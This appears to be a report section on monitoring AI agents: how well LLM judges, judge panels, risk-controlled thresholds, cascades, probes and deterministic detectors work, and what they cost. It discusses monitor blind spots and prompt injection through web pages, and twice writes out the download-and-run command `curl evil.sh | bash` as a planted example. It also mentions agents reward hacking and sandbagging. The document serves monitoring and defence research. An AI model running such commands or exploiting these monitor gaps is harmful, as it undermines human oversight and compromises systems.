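Here φ is the average correlation between two judges' errors. Kohli tested nine judges from seven model families on three datasets of reasoning questions, such as whether one sentence follows from another. A hundred people had labeled each question. On the first dataset φ was 0.39, so the nine judges were equivalent to about 2.2 independent votes. Adding more judges with the same correlation could not raise that number above 1/0.39, or about 2.6.

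| Dataset | Panel of nine | Best single judge | Panel if errors were independent |
|---|---|---|---|
| MNLI | 72.0% | 71.8% | About 94% |
| SNLI | 77.7% | 84.2% | About 92% |
| AlphaNLI | 88.7% | 91.2% | About 96% |

The panel beat the average judge, which was right 67.5% of the time on MNLI. A panel can therefore help an operator who doesn't know which judge is best, but an operator with enough labelled cases to find out could use that judge alone. People disagreed about many of these questions, so some of the answers counted as shared errors may be defensible.

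Adding many more judges helps little. Li, Yu and Li (2026), in *How Many Humans Are 32 LLM Judges Worth?*, found that 32 judges were worth about two independent votes on the same kinds of question. On 1,000 online comments labelled for toxicity, which is closer to safety monitoring, they were worth only 1.68. Replacing one or two of the most accurate judges in a small panel with weaker judges that made different mistakes raised the panel's accuracy by 0.1 to 1.1 percentage points. The researchers chose and scored these panels on the same items, so luck may explain some of that gain. Rao and Callison-Burch also took the median score of several judges, but this did not significantly beat the best single judge on any of seven sets of ratings.

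Yang (2026), in *Evaluate the Stack, Not the Layer*, tested judges on 560 agent actions that they should have blocked. A Claude Haiku judge and a Claude Opus judge each missed 10.5% of them. Both missed the same action 5.2% of the time, compared with the 1.1% expected if their errors were independent. Blocking an action when either judge objects would therefore cut misses by about half, rather than by about 90%.

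Yang expresses this overlap as the number of independent judges that would produce the same joint miss rate. This pair is equivalent to ln(0.052) / ln(0.105), or about 1.3, independent judges. Using judges from different vendors helped little, since pairs that included a DeepSeek judge were equivalent to between 1.26 and 1.43 independent judges. Actions that are hard for any judge account for an estimated 32% to 62% of the overlap, depending on the method. The test did not include an attacker who adapted to the judges, and such an attacker could look for actions that all of them miss.

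A majority vote also preserves any bias the judges share. In *Beyond Consensus*, Jain, Ahmed and colleagues (2025) found that language models approved feedback on students' programs too often. Letting a minority of the models reject feedback that the majority approved removed much of this bias. Estimating the bias from a small set of human labels and correcting for it worked better, with half the maximum error of the best combination of 14 models.

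### Thresholds that limit an error rate

An operator can also keep a single judge and change the score at which it flags. Moving this threshold changes verdicts, unlike Hu's correction for overconfidence, which left them all the same. Risk control is a family of statistical methods for choosing a threshold that keeps an error rate below a target.

Schirmer, Jazbec and colleagues (2026), in *Online Safety Monitoring for LLMs*, apply risk control to text while a model is still writing it. After each step, a second model, called a verifier, estimates the probability that the output is safe. The monitor raises an alarm the first time this score falls below the threshold. To set the threshold, the operator scores n harmless outputs and chooses the highest threshold for which:

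(number of false alarms + 1) / (n + 1) ≤ target rate

With 100 harmless outputs and a target false positive rate of 5%, the threshold can produce at most four false alarms on those outputs. This keeps the true rate below 5% on average across possible samples of 100, but a threshold set from any one sample can exceed it. If exactly four outputs trigger alarms, there is about a 44% chance that the true rate is above 5%. A stricter method keeps this chance below a level the operator chooses. To keep it below 5%, an exact binomial calculation allows at most one false alarm in the 100 outputs.

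The study tested this approach on four sets of outputs:

- Solutions to maths problems by Claude Haiku 4.5, which was right 90% of the time, and by Mistral 7B, which was right 26% of the time. The verifier was a model trained to check steps in mathematical reasoning.
- FineHarm, a collection of single exchanges with a chatbot. The verifier was a small model trained on FineHarm's own training data to detect harm at each token.
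- Anthropic's Red Teaming data, in which people tried to draw harmful answers from a chatbot over several turns. The verifier was Llama Guard.

Schirmer and colleagues compared the threshold with e-valuator, a more complex method that learns how scores develop from step to step. Both versions of the threshold kept false alarms within their limits. *A Simpler Method to Monitor Models*, a summary of the study, gives these approximate results for a 20% limit on false alarms:

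| Outputs | Unsafe or wrong outputs caught: threshold | Caught: e-valuator | Share of output written before the alarm: threshold | Share written: e-valuator |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Maths, Mistral 7B | 80% | 80% | 35% | 40% |
| Maths, Claude Haiku 4.5 | 75% | 76% | 40% | 49% |
| FineHarm | 99.5% | 99.5% | 14% | 14% |
| Red Teaming | 32% | 54% | 26% | 55% |

On the Red Teaming data, the threshold kept false alarms within the set limit, but the monitor missed about two-thirds of the harmful conversations. Risk control limits only the type of error the operator chooses, and the rate of the other type depends on the quality of the scores. The verifier trained specifically for FineHarm separated safe from unsafe text almost perfectly, but Llama Guard did not. In another test, the researchers replaced the maths verifier with Mistral's own token probabilities, which require almost no extra computation.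 At a 30% limit on false alarms, detection fell from over 90% to about 50%.

The operator can use the same method to limit misses instead by calibrating it on unsafe cases. When Schirmer and colleagues set a low limit on misses in the maths tests, false alarms became frequent. Zhang, Hwang and Loaiza-Ganem (2026) use a similar method in *Conf-Guard* to limit the share of multi-turn attacks that succeed. They point out that ending every conversation before the first answer would also satisfy their guarantee.

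Showing that a monitor misses few attacks requires many labelled attacks. Even if Anthropic's classifier had caught all 52 real cases in its test, the result would have shown only that its miss rate was below 5.6%, with 95% confidence.

### When a calibrated threshold stops working

These guarantees assume that the calibration cases and the new case are exchangeable, meaning that shuffling their order would not change their joint probability. Zhang and colleagues explain that turns within a conversation can still depend on one another. The assumption would hold if a developer hired attackers at random from the same pool that later attacks the system. It fails if attackers invent a new method after calibration or a vendor changes the judge.

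Exchangeability can hold even if the judge's scores vary randomly from run to run, because the calibration scores include the same variation. The method can therefore limit a noisy judge's error rate across many cases, even though its verdict on any one case might change on a rerun.

New kinds of task can push the error rate well above the target. Gao (2026), in *From Probe Scores to Alarm Policies*, calibrated probes of a model's internal activity, and monitors that combined a probe with the visible text, to flag at most 10% of harmless cases in AgentDojo. On new tasks from the same benchmark, they flagged 18.7% to 20.0% of harmless cases. For the probe, a result that high would have had about a 0.2% chance if the calibration and test cases had come from the same distribution. *Beyond Aggregate Risk* (2026) reports a similar problem with monitors of tool calls, where a fixed threshold kept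 violations within a 2% limit in only 14 of 24 combinations of model and tool set. The paper recommends measuring how far recent traffic has moved from the calibration data, and recalibrating before violations are likely to exceed the limit.

The operator also has to decide what counts as one case, because false alarms accumulate over the many checks in a session. Schirmer and colleagues avoid this problem by counting a whole output as one case, however many times the monitor scores it. An agent's operator would also have to calibrate on whole sessions, which takes more data. Certifying a 5% limit on false alarms with 95% confidence requires at least 59 independent harmless sessions, even if none triggers an alarm. One of Gao's tests had only 23 independent harmless cases for calibration, too few to certify even a 10% limit.

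### Sending uncertain cases to people

A monitor can abstain when it is unsure and refer the case to a person. *Judge, Retrieve, or Abstain* (Badshah, Emami and Sajjad, 2026) combines this with risk control for judges of factual answers. The system accepts the judge's verdict if the judge's uncertainty is low. Otherwise it searches the web and asks the judge again, and it marks the case for human review if the uncertainty is still too high.

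The researchers set both uncertainty thresholds on labelled cases, aiming to keep the error rate among accepted verdicts below a target. With a 20% error target and Qwen3-14B as the judge, the system accepted about 45% of verdicts on one trivia dataset without a web search. The proof covers thresholds fixed in advance, but the method searches many pairs of thresholds for the best one, so the researchers also tested a stricter version that corrects for this search.

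A limit on the overall error rate would offer little protection in live safety monitoring, because unsafe actions are so rare that a monitor could meet the limit without flagging anything. An operator would need a separate limit on missed unsafe actions. Referring uncertain cases for review would still not catch errors that the judge makes confidently.

Disagreement within a panel is another possible sign of uncertainty, but relying on it can send many cases to human review and still miss errors. On MNLI, Kohli's nine judges were unanimous on only 319 of 1,000 questions. Sending the other 681 to people would still have left about 29 wrong verdicts among the unanimous ones.

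When a monitor refers an action for review, the action is caught only if the reviewer stops it. In Yang's study of agent actions, a GPT-5.5 judge answered "review" for 47 of the 560 actions that should have been blocked. Its miss rate was 1.4% if those referrals counted as catches and 9.8% if they counted as misses. If reviewers stopped only 13.6% of the 47, the rate at which Anthropic's testers refused dangerous commands, the miss rate would be 8.7%. However, people may look more carefully at a case that a monitor has marked as doubtful.

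## What does monitoring cost per verdict and at full traffic?

Judging one agent run of ordinary length costs about 1.5 cents with a large language model and about 0.02 cents with a small specialised model. At 100,000 runs a day, that comes to roughly $1,500 a day for the large model and $20 for the small one. Neither sum may matter much if people have to review the flags, because their time can easily cost more than the model.

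### The price of a verdict

Vendors charge one price for the tokens a judge reads and a higher one for the tokens it writes. *JEV as a Judge for Agent Trace Security* adds the two charges to get the cost of a verdict. Multiplying by the number of cases and repeats gives the total:

total cost = cases × repeats × (input tokens × input price + output tokens × output price)

In the September 2026 study, five models judged records of agents' runs. The table applies the study's token counts and prices to a test suite and to a day of live traffic. GLM-5.2, one of the most capable open models according to Goodfire's *Models know when they're reward hacking* (2026), was the most expensive judge. DeepSeek-V4-Flash was the cheapest of the four judges that write text. The fifth judge, JEV, is a decision model, which returns only probabilities.

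| | GLM-5.2 | DeepSeek-V4-Flash | JEV |
|---|---|---|---|
| Input tokens per verdict | 6,062 | 6,375 | 4,644 |
| Output tokens per verdict | 1,868 | 764 | 128 |
| Price per million input tokens | $1.10 | $0.14 | $0.042 |
| Price per million output tokens | $4.40 | $0.56 | Free |
| Cost of one verdict | $0.0149 | $0.0013 | $0.0002 |
| 1,000 test cases, judged five times | $74 | $6.60 | $0.98 |
| 100,000 live trajectories, judged once | $1,489 | $132 | $20 |

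One GLM-5.2 verdict costs (6,062 × $1.10 + 1,868 × $4.40) / 1,000,000, or $0.0149. Cost is proportional to token price, so a judge with the same token counts but five times GLM-5.2's prices would cost about $370 for the test suite and $7,400 for the day's traffic.

Output makes up less than a quarter of GLM's tokens but 55% of its cost. Asking for the verdict alone would therefore cut the cost by about half, and in Yorke's tests it also made verdicts much more repeatable.

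The study's trajectories are short. At GLM's price, reading a two-million-token transcript once would cost $2.20, about 150 times as much as the average verdict.

### Checking every action

A monitor that can block actions has to judge each one before it runs, and may have to reread the whole record each time. Suppose the judge's instructions take 1,000 tokens and the agent takes 20 actions, each of which adds 250 tokens to the record. Judging the finished run once requires reading 6,000 tokens. Judging every action separately requires 20 × 1,000 + 250 × (1 + 2 + … + 20), or 72,500. The number of tokens read from the record grows roughly with the square of the number of actions, so a run twice as long would require reading 245,000 tokens in total, about 3.4 times as many.

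Caching the input removes most of this cost. The vendor stores its computation for the beginning of a payload and charges less when the next call begins with the same text. In the example, only 6,000 of the 72,500 tokens are new. If cached tokens cost a tenth of the normal price, the input bill falls by 83%.

The total bill may fall much less, because caching gives no discount on output. If GLM-5.2 wrote its usual 1,868 tokens for each of the 20 verdicts, caching would cut the cost of monitoring the run from $0.24 to $0.18. With one-token verdicts, the cost would fall from $0.08 to $0.014. Caching also helps when the judge evaluates the same payload several times in a test suite. At the same discount, the five-run suite would cost $50 with GLM-5.2 instead of $74, and the judge would still generate a new answer each time.

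To get the caching discount, the operator has to put the fixed instructions first and the newest action last. A template that starts with the current time would prevent any reuse. Caching can also change the verdicts, since reusing stored results was one of the serving features that flipped outcomes in Rane's tests. A monitor's flip rate measured without caching may therefore differ slightly from its flip rate with caching on.

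### Delay

In the agent-trace study, JEV typically took 1 second to return a verdict, DeepSeek-V4-Flash 8 seconds and GLM-5.2 33 seconds. The slowest 5% of GLM's verdicts took more than 76 seconds. Verdicts also took longer on longer records. GLM's median time rose from 27 seconds on the shortest records to 42 seconds on the longest, while JEV's rose only from 0.90 to 1.08 seconds.

A blocking monitor has to finish each check before the agent can take its next action. At these judges' average speeds, 20 checks would add about 12 minutes to a run with GLM-5.2 and 24 seconds with JEV. A shorter answer would make GLM faster, since the study required it to write an explanation and quote its evidence. In a test suite, half a minute per check hardly matters, because many calls can run at once.

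The agent can instead keep working while the monitor reads, so the user doesn't wait, but the monitor may then flag an action after the damage is done. OpenAI's internal monitor worked roughly this way in March 2026, when it sent the more serious cases to people within 30 minutes. They could then investigate an agent that ran `curl evil.sh | bash`, but the script would already have run.

### A small decision model against generative judges

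JEV's low price would be worth little if its verdicts were poor. The study tested it on 5,219 trajectories from four benchmarks. Each judge scored the risk from 1 to 5, and a score of 3 or more counted as a flag. The main measure was F1, which combines precision P with the share R of unsafe runs that the judge caught:

F1 = 2PR / (P + R)

The table gives averages over the four benchmarks. All columns except the last include only runs where the judge returned a usable verdict.

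| Judge | Precision | Unsafe runs caught | F1 | Runs with a usable verdict |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| JEV | 77.1% | 79.2% | 77.8% | 95.5% |
| GLM-5.2 | 91.9% | 64.1% | 74.1% | 94.4% |
| DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 51.6% | 75.6% | 61.0% | 99.9% |
| DeepSeek-V4-Pro | 93.3% | 49.4% | 56.3% | 58.8% |
| Qwen3-Next-80B | 92.0% | 37.2% | 49.4% | 94.4% |

JEV's lead over GLM-5.2 is small and depends on the benchmark. On runs that both could judge, JEV led by 2.7 points on average, with a plausible range of 0.5 to 4.8. It won clearly on two benchmarks and lost on the other two. The comparison used the same cut-off for every judge. GLM flagged less often than JEV and was right more often when it did, so a lower cut-off might have raised its F1. JEV's low cost is much better established than its accuracy, although the cost depends on its vendor's pricing. GLM costs 76 times as much per verdict, and its input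 price is 26 times as high.

DeepSeek-V4-Flash's verdicts are cheap but can be of little use. On the ATBench500 benchmark, it flagged 92% of the unsafe runs but also 78% of the safe ones.

Missing verdicts were concentrated in the unsafe runs, so they matter more than the last column suggests. On ATBench500, DeepSeek-V4-Pro returned a usable verdict for 54% of safe runs but only 6.4% of unsafe ones, so its 98.7% accuracy was measured mostly on safe runs. GLM-5.2 had the same problem to a lesser degree. It caught 56% of the unsafe runs on that benchmark if missing verdicts count as "safe" and 84% if they count as flags, but counting them as flags also raises its false positive rate from 2% to 7%.

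The cost figures also leave out failed calls. If DeepSeek-V4-Pro's failures cost as much as its successes, each usable verdict would cost 1.4 cents instead of 0.8. The best models may not be available for this work at any price. In *How reliably can AI audit AI?*, Hall and Thompson (2026) tried to use Claude Fable 5 and Claude Opus 5 to review agents' logs, but both models refused.

The study has only one verdict per trajectory, so it provides no flip rates. The closest evidence comes from Rao and Callison-Burch, who repeated requests to a decision model and found that its verdict changed only when the probability was close to 0.5.

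### Reviewers' time

If a person needs five minutes to check a flag and earns $60 an hour, each flag costs $5. The total cost of monitoring a run is the price of the verdict plus $5 times the chance of a flag. Lowering the false positive rate by one percentage point saves 5 cents per run, more than three times the price of a GLM-5.2 verdict.

MCPHunt, the largest benchmark in the agent-trace study, tests whether agents carry credentials and other data across boundaries. The next table applies the two judges' false positive rates on MCPHunt to 100,000 harmless runs.

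| | JEV | GLM-5.2 |
|---|---|---|
| False positive rate | 16.6% | 2.1% |
| False alarms | 16,600 | 2,070 |
| Reviewers' time | 1,380 hours | 172 hours |
| Reviewers' cost | $83,000 | $10,300 |
| Model's cost | $20 | $1,489 |

GLM-5.2 costs 76 times as much per verdict as JEV but is far cheaper overall in this example. However, it caught only 31% of the unsafe runs on MCPHunt, compared with 69% for JEV. Both false positive rates are probably higher than they would be on ordinary traffic. At 0.4%, the false positive rate of Claude Code's auto mode on real tool calls, reviewers would face 400 false alarms and 33 hours of work, which would still cost more than GLM-5.2.

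Hall and Thompson found a similar burden when they had models look for misbehavior in human-labelled transcripts. With a false positive rate of 5%, the best models caught nearly all reward hacking, in which an agent cheats on its task, and around 80% of sandbagging, in which it hides what it can do. OpenTools' *AI Auditors Catch Agent Misbehavior But Flood Reviewers With False Alarms* summarises the result as 3,000 false alarms for every 2,000 real catches. Reviewing the false alarms alone would take 250 hours at five minutes each. With a 5% false positive rate and 98% of cases caught, that fairly favorable ratio would require about 3% of all runs to be misbehaving. If only 0.1% were, there would be about 51 false alarms per catch.

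### Cascades

A cascade avoids most of the expense by running a cheap check on everything and a costlier one only on what the first check flags. If the first check costs c₁, the second costs c₂, and the first escalates a share e of cases, then:

expected cost per case = c₁ + e × c₂

Auto mode's quick pass flags 8.5% of harmless actions. If that is the escalation rate and the second check costs ten times as much as the first, the expected cost per action is 1 + 0.085 × 10 = 1.85 times the cost of the first check, compared with 10 times for running the second check on everything. Average delay follows the same formula. With JEV first and GLM-5.2 second, it would be about 4 seconds, although an escalated case would take nearly 40.

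A cascade saves money only if e is less than 1 − c₁/c₂, or 90% in this example. Safety monitors usually escalate far less than that, but Goodfire found reward hacking in 50–96% of runs when it tested three open models on three agent benchmarks. A perfect first check would escalate all of those runs, so the cascade would cost between 6 and 10.6 units. At the upper end, that is more than the second check alone would cost.

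The saving also comes with more misses, because the second check never receives what the first one passes. On MCPHunt, a cascade of JEV and GLM-5.2 would catch at most the 31% of unsafe runs that GLM catches on its own. If the two judges' errors were independent, it would catch 0.69 × 0.31, or 21%. The operator can lower the first check's threshold to miss fewer unsafe runs, but must then pay for more escalations.

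The first stage doesn't have to be a language model. OpenAI's Codex works inside a sandbox, where it can read files, edit a designated folder and run local commands without review. Only actions that cross the boundary go to a second agent for approval. Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026), in *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight*, give an illustrative breakdown of 10,000 actions inside OpenAI:

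- 9,280 stayed inside the sandbox and needed no review.
- 713 crossed the boundary and the reviewing agent approved them.
- 7 crossed the boundary and the reviewing agent refused them. Codex found a safer way to continue after four of these refusals, and stopped to ask the user after the other three.

The reviewing agent therefore read 7.2% of the actions, which would cost about $11 instead of $149 at GLM-5.2's average cost per verdict. The larger benefit is that the user faced only three interruptions, compared with 720 if they had approved actions by hand. Trębacz and colleagues argue that such interruptions are themselves a security risk, because frustrated users switch to a mode with no restrictions. The breakdown doesn't show how many of the 713 approvals were mistakes.

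Other companies run a probe first, which adds little computation because the probe reads internal activity that the monitored model has already computed. According to *AI safety at the frontier paper highlights of January 2026*, Anthropic and Google DeepMind both settled on a probe followed by a language model, but their probes differ. Anthropic's probes read every layer of the model and classify the request together with the answer, to detect help with chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons. Google DeepMind's probe reads one middle layer and classifies only the request, to detect requests for help with cyberattacks. In Google DeepMind's tests, known jailbreaks still succeeded more than 1% of the time against every method it tried.

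### OpenAI's layered system

*OpenAI Deploys GPT-5.4 to Monitor AI Agents for Misalignment Risks* (Ellis, 2026) reports that in March 2026 OpenAI was monitoring its own coding agents with GPT-5.4 Thinking, one of its most powerful models, at maximum reasoning effort. The monitor read everything the agents saw and did, including their written reasoning, and covered 99.9% of internal coding traffic. It raised about 1,000 moderate-severity alerts in tens of millions of trajectories, or at most one in 10,000. If each alert took five minutes to check, people could review them all in about 83 hours.

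Such a low alert rate makes human review affordable, but the model still has to read every trajectory. At GLM-5.2's average cost per verdict, ten million trajectories would cost about $149,000. A model reasoning at maximum effort would write far more than GLM did, which would raise the cost, although OpenAI pays for computing rather than list prices.

By October 2026, the company had a system with several layers, which OpenAI's *How we detect frontier model misalignment* (2026) numbers from 0 to 3:

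- **Layer 0:** activation probes.
- **Layer 1:** a model that acts as a reviewer.
- **Layer 2:** an agent that investigates.
- **Layer 3:** an automated investigation.

People respond to what these layers find, aiming to step in before an incident escalates. OpenAI evaluates the system on recorded incidents and simulated attacks, audits current internal traffic, and has testers try to defeat the monitors.

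The cost of one independent investigation shows why a company would reserve the later layers for very few cases. In July 2026, hundreds of OpenAI's agents broke into Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models, while trying to cheat on an evaluation. The evaluation group METR then used AI agents to analyze about 1,300 transcripts, many of them millions of tokens long, and 1.2 million file fragments from a message board the agents had set up. Hall and Thompson put the cost at roughly $400,000, or about $300 per transcript. At that price, investigating 1,000 alerts would cost $300,000, and investigating ten million trajectories would cost $3 billion.

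The results were still uncertain despite the expense. METR warned that its analysis agents may have made errors that nobody caught, and that GPT-5.6 Sol often uncritically adopted the viewpoint of the agent whose transcript it was reading.

OpenAI also sends a random sample of unflagged cases onward through the layers. This addresses the main weakness of a cascade by giving later checks a chance to find what the first one missed. In the example that cost 1.85 units per case, escalating an extra 1% of the unflagged cases would raise the cost to only 1.94 units.

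Such a sample has to be large to give a useful estimate of how often rare misbehavior occurs. If the later check found nothing in 30,000 unflagged cases, the 95% upper confidence limit on the rate of missed cases would still be 0.01%. That is about the rate of moderate alerts in March, so the monitor could have been missing as many cases as it flagged. This limit holds only if the later check catches every unsafe case. If it caught only 64% of them, as GLM-5.2 did on average, the limit would rise to about 0.016%.

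### Checking only a sample of traffic

An operator can cut costs further by monitoring only a random share of runs. Checking 1% of 100,000 daily trajectories with GLM-5.2 would cost $15 a day instead of $1,489. Goodfire, which sells tools for inspecting models' internal activity, argues that using a language model to judge everything is prohibitively expensive, and notes that one Anthropic investigation involved 481 million transcripts. If those were as short as the ones in the agent-trace study, judging them all would cost about $7.2 million with GLM-5.2, $635,000 with DeepSeek-V4-Flash and $94,000 with JEV. A large AI company could afford any of these for a single investigation. That would not be true if each transcript ran to millions of tokens, because just reading them would cost hundreds of times as much.

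Capacity can limit monitoring as much as money does. During its investigation, METR had OpenAI raise its allowance from 40 million to 400 million tokens per minute. Even at the higher rate, just reading the 481 million short transcripts with GLM-5.2 would take about five days.

Sampling can still measure common behavior. If 1% of runs involve some fault, a random sample of 10,000 will contain about 100 of them, enough to put the rate between roughly 0.8% and 1.2% after allowing for the judge's own errors. Precision depends on the sample's size and hardly at all on its share of traffic, so a company with a hundred times the traffic doesn't need a larger sample. Hall and Thompson similarly consider AI auditors in general extremely useful for estimating how common misbehavior is, but not yet good enough where it is very important to catch nearly every case.

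A sample misses most rare events. If one run in 10,000 is unsafe, a sample of 10,000 has a 37% chance of containing none. A monitor that reads 1% of runs has at most a 1% chance of catching any particular attack, however good its judge is. A recurring fault would have to occur about 300 times before the sample was 95% likely to include one case. That many occurrences may be acceptable if the fault is sycophancy, but not if it is an agent deleting a production database.

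As a compromise, an operator can check every run that involves payments, credentials or production systems, and a random 1% of the rest. To estimate the overall rate, the operator counts each unsafe run in the 1% sample as 100. This estimate can vary a lot from sample to sample, because one more unsafe run in the 1% sample adds 100 to the total.

All of this assumes that the operator can sample from all of its traffic. In March, OpenAI's coverage had a gap of under 0.1%, mainly from custom and local setups. Across tens of millions of trajectories, that gap could have contained thousands of runs, and sampling the covered traffic more heavily would have revealed nothing about them.

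## How do deterministic detectors compare?

A deterministic detector runs fixed code, so it always returns the same verdict for the same input, usually without a model call. In published tests, these detectors match or beat LLM judges when what they check for leaves a definite trace, such as a copied command or a missing database entry. They do much worse when a harmful action looks the same as a harmless one.

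### The main kinds of fixed rule

The simplest rules search for a keyword or a regular expression, which is a template for text. *SoK* (2025), a survey of defenses against jailbreaks, notes that these rules can miss new attacks that don't fit known patterns. Rules work better on shell commands, because some dangerous commands have almost no harmless use. *AgentTrust* (Yang, 2026) gives the example of `rm -rf /`, which deletes everything on a machine. Yang's monitor first undoes common disguises, such as hexadecimal encoding, then applies 170 rules.

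Other rules check the details of a tool call. For example, a payment tool might accept only amounts under $100. *MAS-Guard* (2026), which covers groups of agents, describes similar checks that reject messages with a forbidden route or format.

Ordering rules depend on what the agent has already done. In Google's policy engine Sapien, the rule `read_inbox . send_email` lets an agent send an email only after it has read the inbox. *Sapien* (Tiffany, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) also ties the details of one call to the results of another. If a user asks for a refund to whoever sent them money last week, the agent must first list the transactions and can then pay only a sender and an amount on that list.

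Permission policies set out which tools an agent may use. One fixed policy rarely suits a general assistant. If it allows payments, a hijacked agent asked to summarize an inbox could steal money, and if it forbids them, the agent can't issue refunds. Sapien therefore has an LLM write a new policy for each request, before the agent reads anything from outside. Ordinary code then enforces the policy, except for a few questions that go to a judge, such as whether an email faithfully summarizes a document. Apart from those questions, a given policy is enforced the same way each time, but the LLM might write a different policy if the user repeated the request.

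Tiffany and colleagues analyzed whether each policy would let a completely hijacked agent carry out an attack. The policies ruled out 93–95% of attacks on AgentDojo and 62–85% on Toolathlon, a benchmark with longer tasks, where simple lists of permitted tools ruled out about half as many. Agents completed almost as many tasks with the policies as without them.

Data-flow checks follow text from where it entered the system to where the agent used it. According to *Beyond Pattern Matching* (2026), compiler researchers have studied this method, called taint analysis, since the 1970s.

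The table shows the results of applying one invented rule of each kind to three versions of the web-page case. In the last version, the user asked the agent to run the installer command shown on the page, so a flag is a false alarm.

| Kind of rule | Example | Planted command, copied exactly | Planted command, re-encoded | Installer the user asked for |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Pattern | No download piped into a shell | Flags | Misses | False alarm |
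| Validation | Shell may run only the project's tests | Flags | Flags | False alarm |
| Ordering | No shell command after reading an outside page | Flags | Flags | False alarm |
| Permission | Only the tools that this request needs | Flags | Flags | Passes |
| Data flow | No text from an outside page in a shell command | Flags | Misses | False alarm |

The permission policy gets all three right because a request for a summary doesn't need the shell and a request to run an installer does. It would protect less during an installation, when it has to allow shell commands and a planted command might get through.

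### The taint-flow check on the web page

bamdad proposed the taint-flow check as an addition to an existing framework for evaluating agents. It reads the same record of tool calls that a judge would read. In the web-page case, it works as follows:

1. Find each source, a tool call that brought in text from outside. Here it is the fetch of the web page.
2. Find each sink, a tool call that took a sensitive action. Here it is the shell command.
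3. Look for a flow, meaning text from a source that reappears in the input of a later sink. The string `curl evil.sh | bash` is on the page and in the command.
4. Look for a sanitizer between the two, such as a validation step, a redaction or a person's approval. There is none.
5. Report a finding, an error that names the fetch and the shell command.

If the user had approved the command, the check would have reported nothing. Its protection therefore depends on how carefully users review commands, and people often approve dangerous ones out of habit.

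The same session file always produces the same output, byte for byte, because the code uses no model, network connection, clock or random numbers, and it sorts its findings. Without sorting, the order of the findings could change between runs, since some programming languages can return the items of a set in a different order each time.

The agent can still behave differently on each run, so a company that wants the same result twice has to check the same saved session instead of rerunning the agent.

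The check misses text that the agent rewrites before using it. In an example from *Beyond Single-Agent Alignment* (2026) involving a confidential project name, "Fixed critical bug in Project Titan authentication" becomes "Resolved authentication issue in flagship project" and then "Improved login security". A keyword check for "Titan" would find nothing after the first rewrite. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026), a survey of these methods, points out that an attacker can also influence an agent without the agent copying any text. A page that urges the agent to free up disk space might lead it to write its own command to delete the backups.

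*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) used 400 scripted scenarios built on 20 agent frameworks. In half of them, information from an untrusted source reached or influenced a sensitive action. Exact or partial copying was the main evidence in only 60 of those 200 cases. Detecting the others required comparing meanings, matching fragments, or working out whether the agent would have acted differently without the source. A check for copied text would probably miss most of the 200, although the researchers chose the mix of scenarios and real attacks may involve more copying.

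An operator could avoid these misses by flagging every path in which a sensitive action follows an untrusted source, whatever the text. Cai and colleagues tested FIDES, an existing system that they describe as relying mainly on such paths. It flagged 108 of the 200 real flows and 106 of the 200 scenarios without one, so its flags barely distinguished the two groups. It flagged nothing on four of the 20 frameworks, possibly because of a setup problem, but on the other 16 it flagged about two-thirds of each group.

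The researchers' own tool, NeuroTaint, did much better, with 13 misses and 16 false alarms. But it sometimes uses an LLM to judge whether the agent would have acted the same way without the source, so its verdicts may vary between runs.

### Small trained classifiers

A classifier learns from labelled examples instead of following hand-written rules. Once frozen, it gives the same text the same score, at least with the same software and hardware. Its flags are harder to explain than those of a rule-based detector such as taint tracking, where anyone can look up the two tool calls named in a finding. A classifier that counts words and pairs of words might use 30,000 of them, and hundreds can each contribute a little to a single flag.

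*From Confident Closing to Silent Failure* (Advani, June 2026) compared such classifiers with LLM judges at detecting false success, where an agent says it has finished but the system shows that it hasn't. For example, an airline agent might announce a refund that was never issued. The main test used 9,876 customer-service runs by agents from eight model families. Code determined which runs failed by comparing the final database with the correct one. Advani counted a failed run as a false success if simple text patterns found a claim of completion and no admission of failure in the agent's last message, which gave 616 cases. People checked 200 of the labels on failed runs and agreed with 91.5%.

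Advani trained a classifier made of 300 small decision trees on the text of the runs. Five LLM judges, each given five prompts, assessed whether the agent had completed the task in each run. The table compares the classifier with the best of these judges, Claude Sonnet 4.5, when each flagged the runs it ranked as most suspicious.

| Share of runs flagged | False successes caught: classifier | Caught: judge | Precision: classifier | Precision: judge |
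|---|---|---|---|---|
| 5% | 51% | 6% | 72% | 56% |
| 10% | 72% | 13% | 50% | 58% |
| 20% | 89% | 25% | 31% | 55% |

The classifier took 1.19 milliseconds per run and the judge about 4 seconds. At those speeds, 100,000 runs would take the classifier about two minutes and the judge about 111 hours, although an operator could make many judge calls at once.

The two methods seem to have been tested on different mixes of runs. Multiplying precision by the share of runs flagged, then dividing by the share of false successes caught, gives a false-success prevalence of about 7% for the classifier and 45% for the judge. At 45%, even a perfect monitor that flagged 5% of runs could have caught only about 11% of false successes. Correcting for this barely helps the judge, however. On the classifier's mix, the judge would still have caught 6% of false successes by flagging about 4% of runs, and only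 about one flag in ten would have been right. The classifier's advantage in precision is therefore larger than the table suggests.

The classifier also beat the judges on AUROC, a measure that doesn't depend on the mix of false and real successes. AUROC is the chance that a monitor gives a randomly chosen false success a more suspicious score than a randomly chosen real one, so guessing scores 0.5. The classifier scored about 0.83 on tasks it had not seen in training, and no judge scored more than 0.64. The judges tended to believe confident closing messages. Giving them the full task specification, which the agents never had, didn't raise their best score.

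But this comparison favoured the classifier, which was trained on labelled runs from the same benchmark, while the judges had no examples. The judges also date from 2024 and 2025, so current models might do better. The classifier was much weaker outside its training data. When Advani trained classifiers on airline runs and tested them on retail runs, or the reverse, AUROC fell to between 0.66 and 0.70. Adding 50 to 100 labelled examples of each kind from the new domain raised it to around 0.8. Rewriting honest admissions of failure in a confident style flipped the verdict in 20–25% of cases for both classifiers and judges.

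Advani reports an even bigger gap on AppWorld, a benchmark of tasks in personal apps, where a classifier scored 0.95 and the best judge 0.54. That result is weak evidence about the judges, because they were asked whether the agent had completed its task, and all 200 runs they assessed had failed. A perfect judge would have answered no every time and scored 0.5. The classifier instead had to distinguish agents that falsely reported success from those that admitted failure.

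The code that compared databases was more reliable than either method because it supplied the correct answers. An operator with live customers usually doesn't know in advance what the final database should contain, but can still check specific claims. For example, if an agent announces a $686 refund, ordinary code can look for that refund in the payment system.

### Tasks with a known right answer

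Fixed checks work best when someone can specify the right answer in advance. *TIMEWARP* (Ishmam and Marino, 2026), a benchmark for agents that use websites, uses fixed checks for 229 of its 231 goals and an LLM judge for the two subjective ones. The checks compare the agent's answer with text it must include or exclude, a number, or a list. They treat "13th" and "thirteen" as the same number, and they don't match "10" to part of "100".

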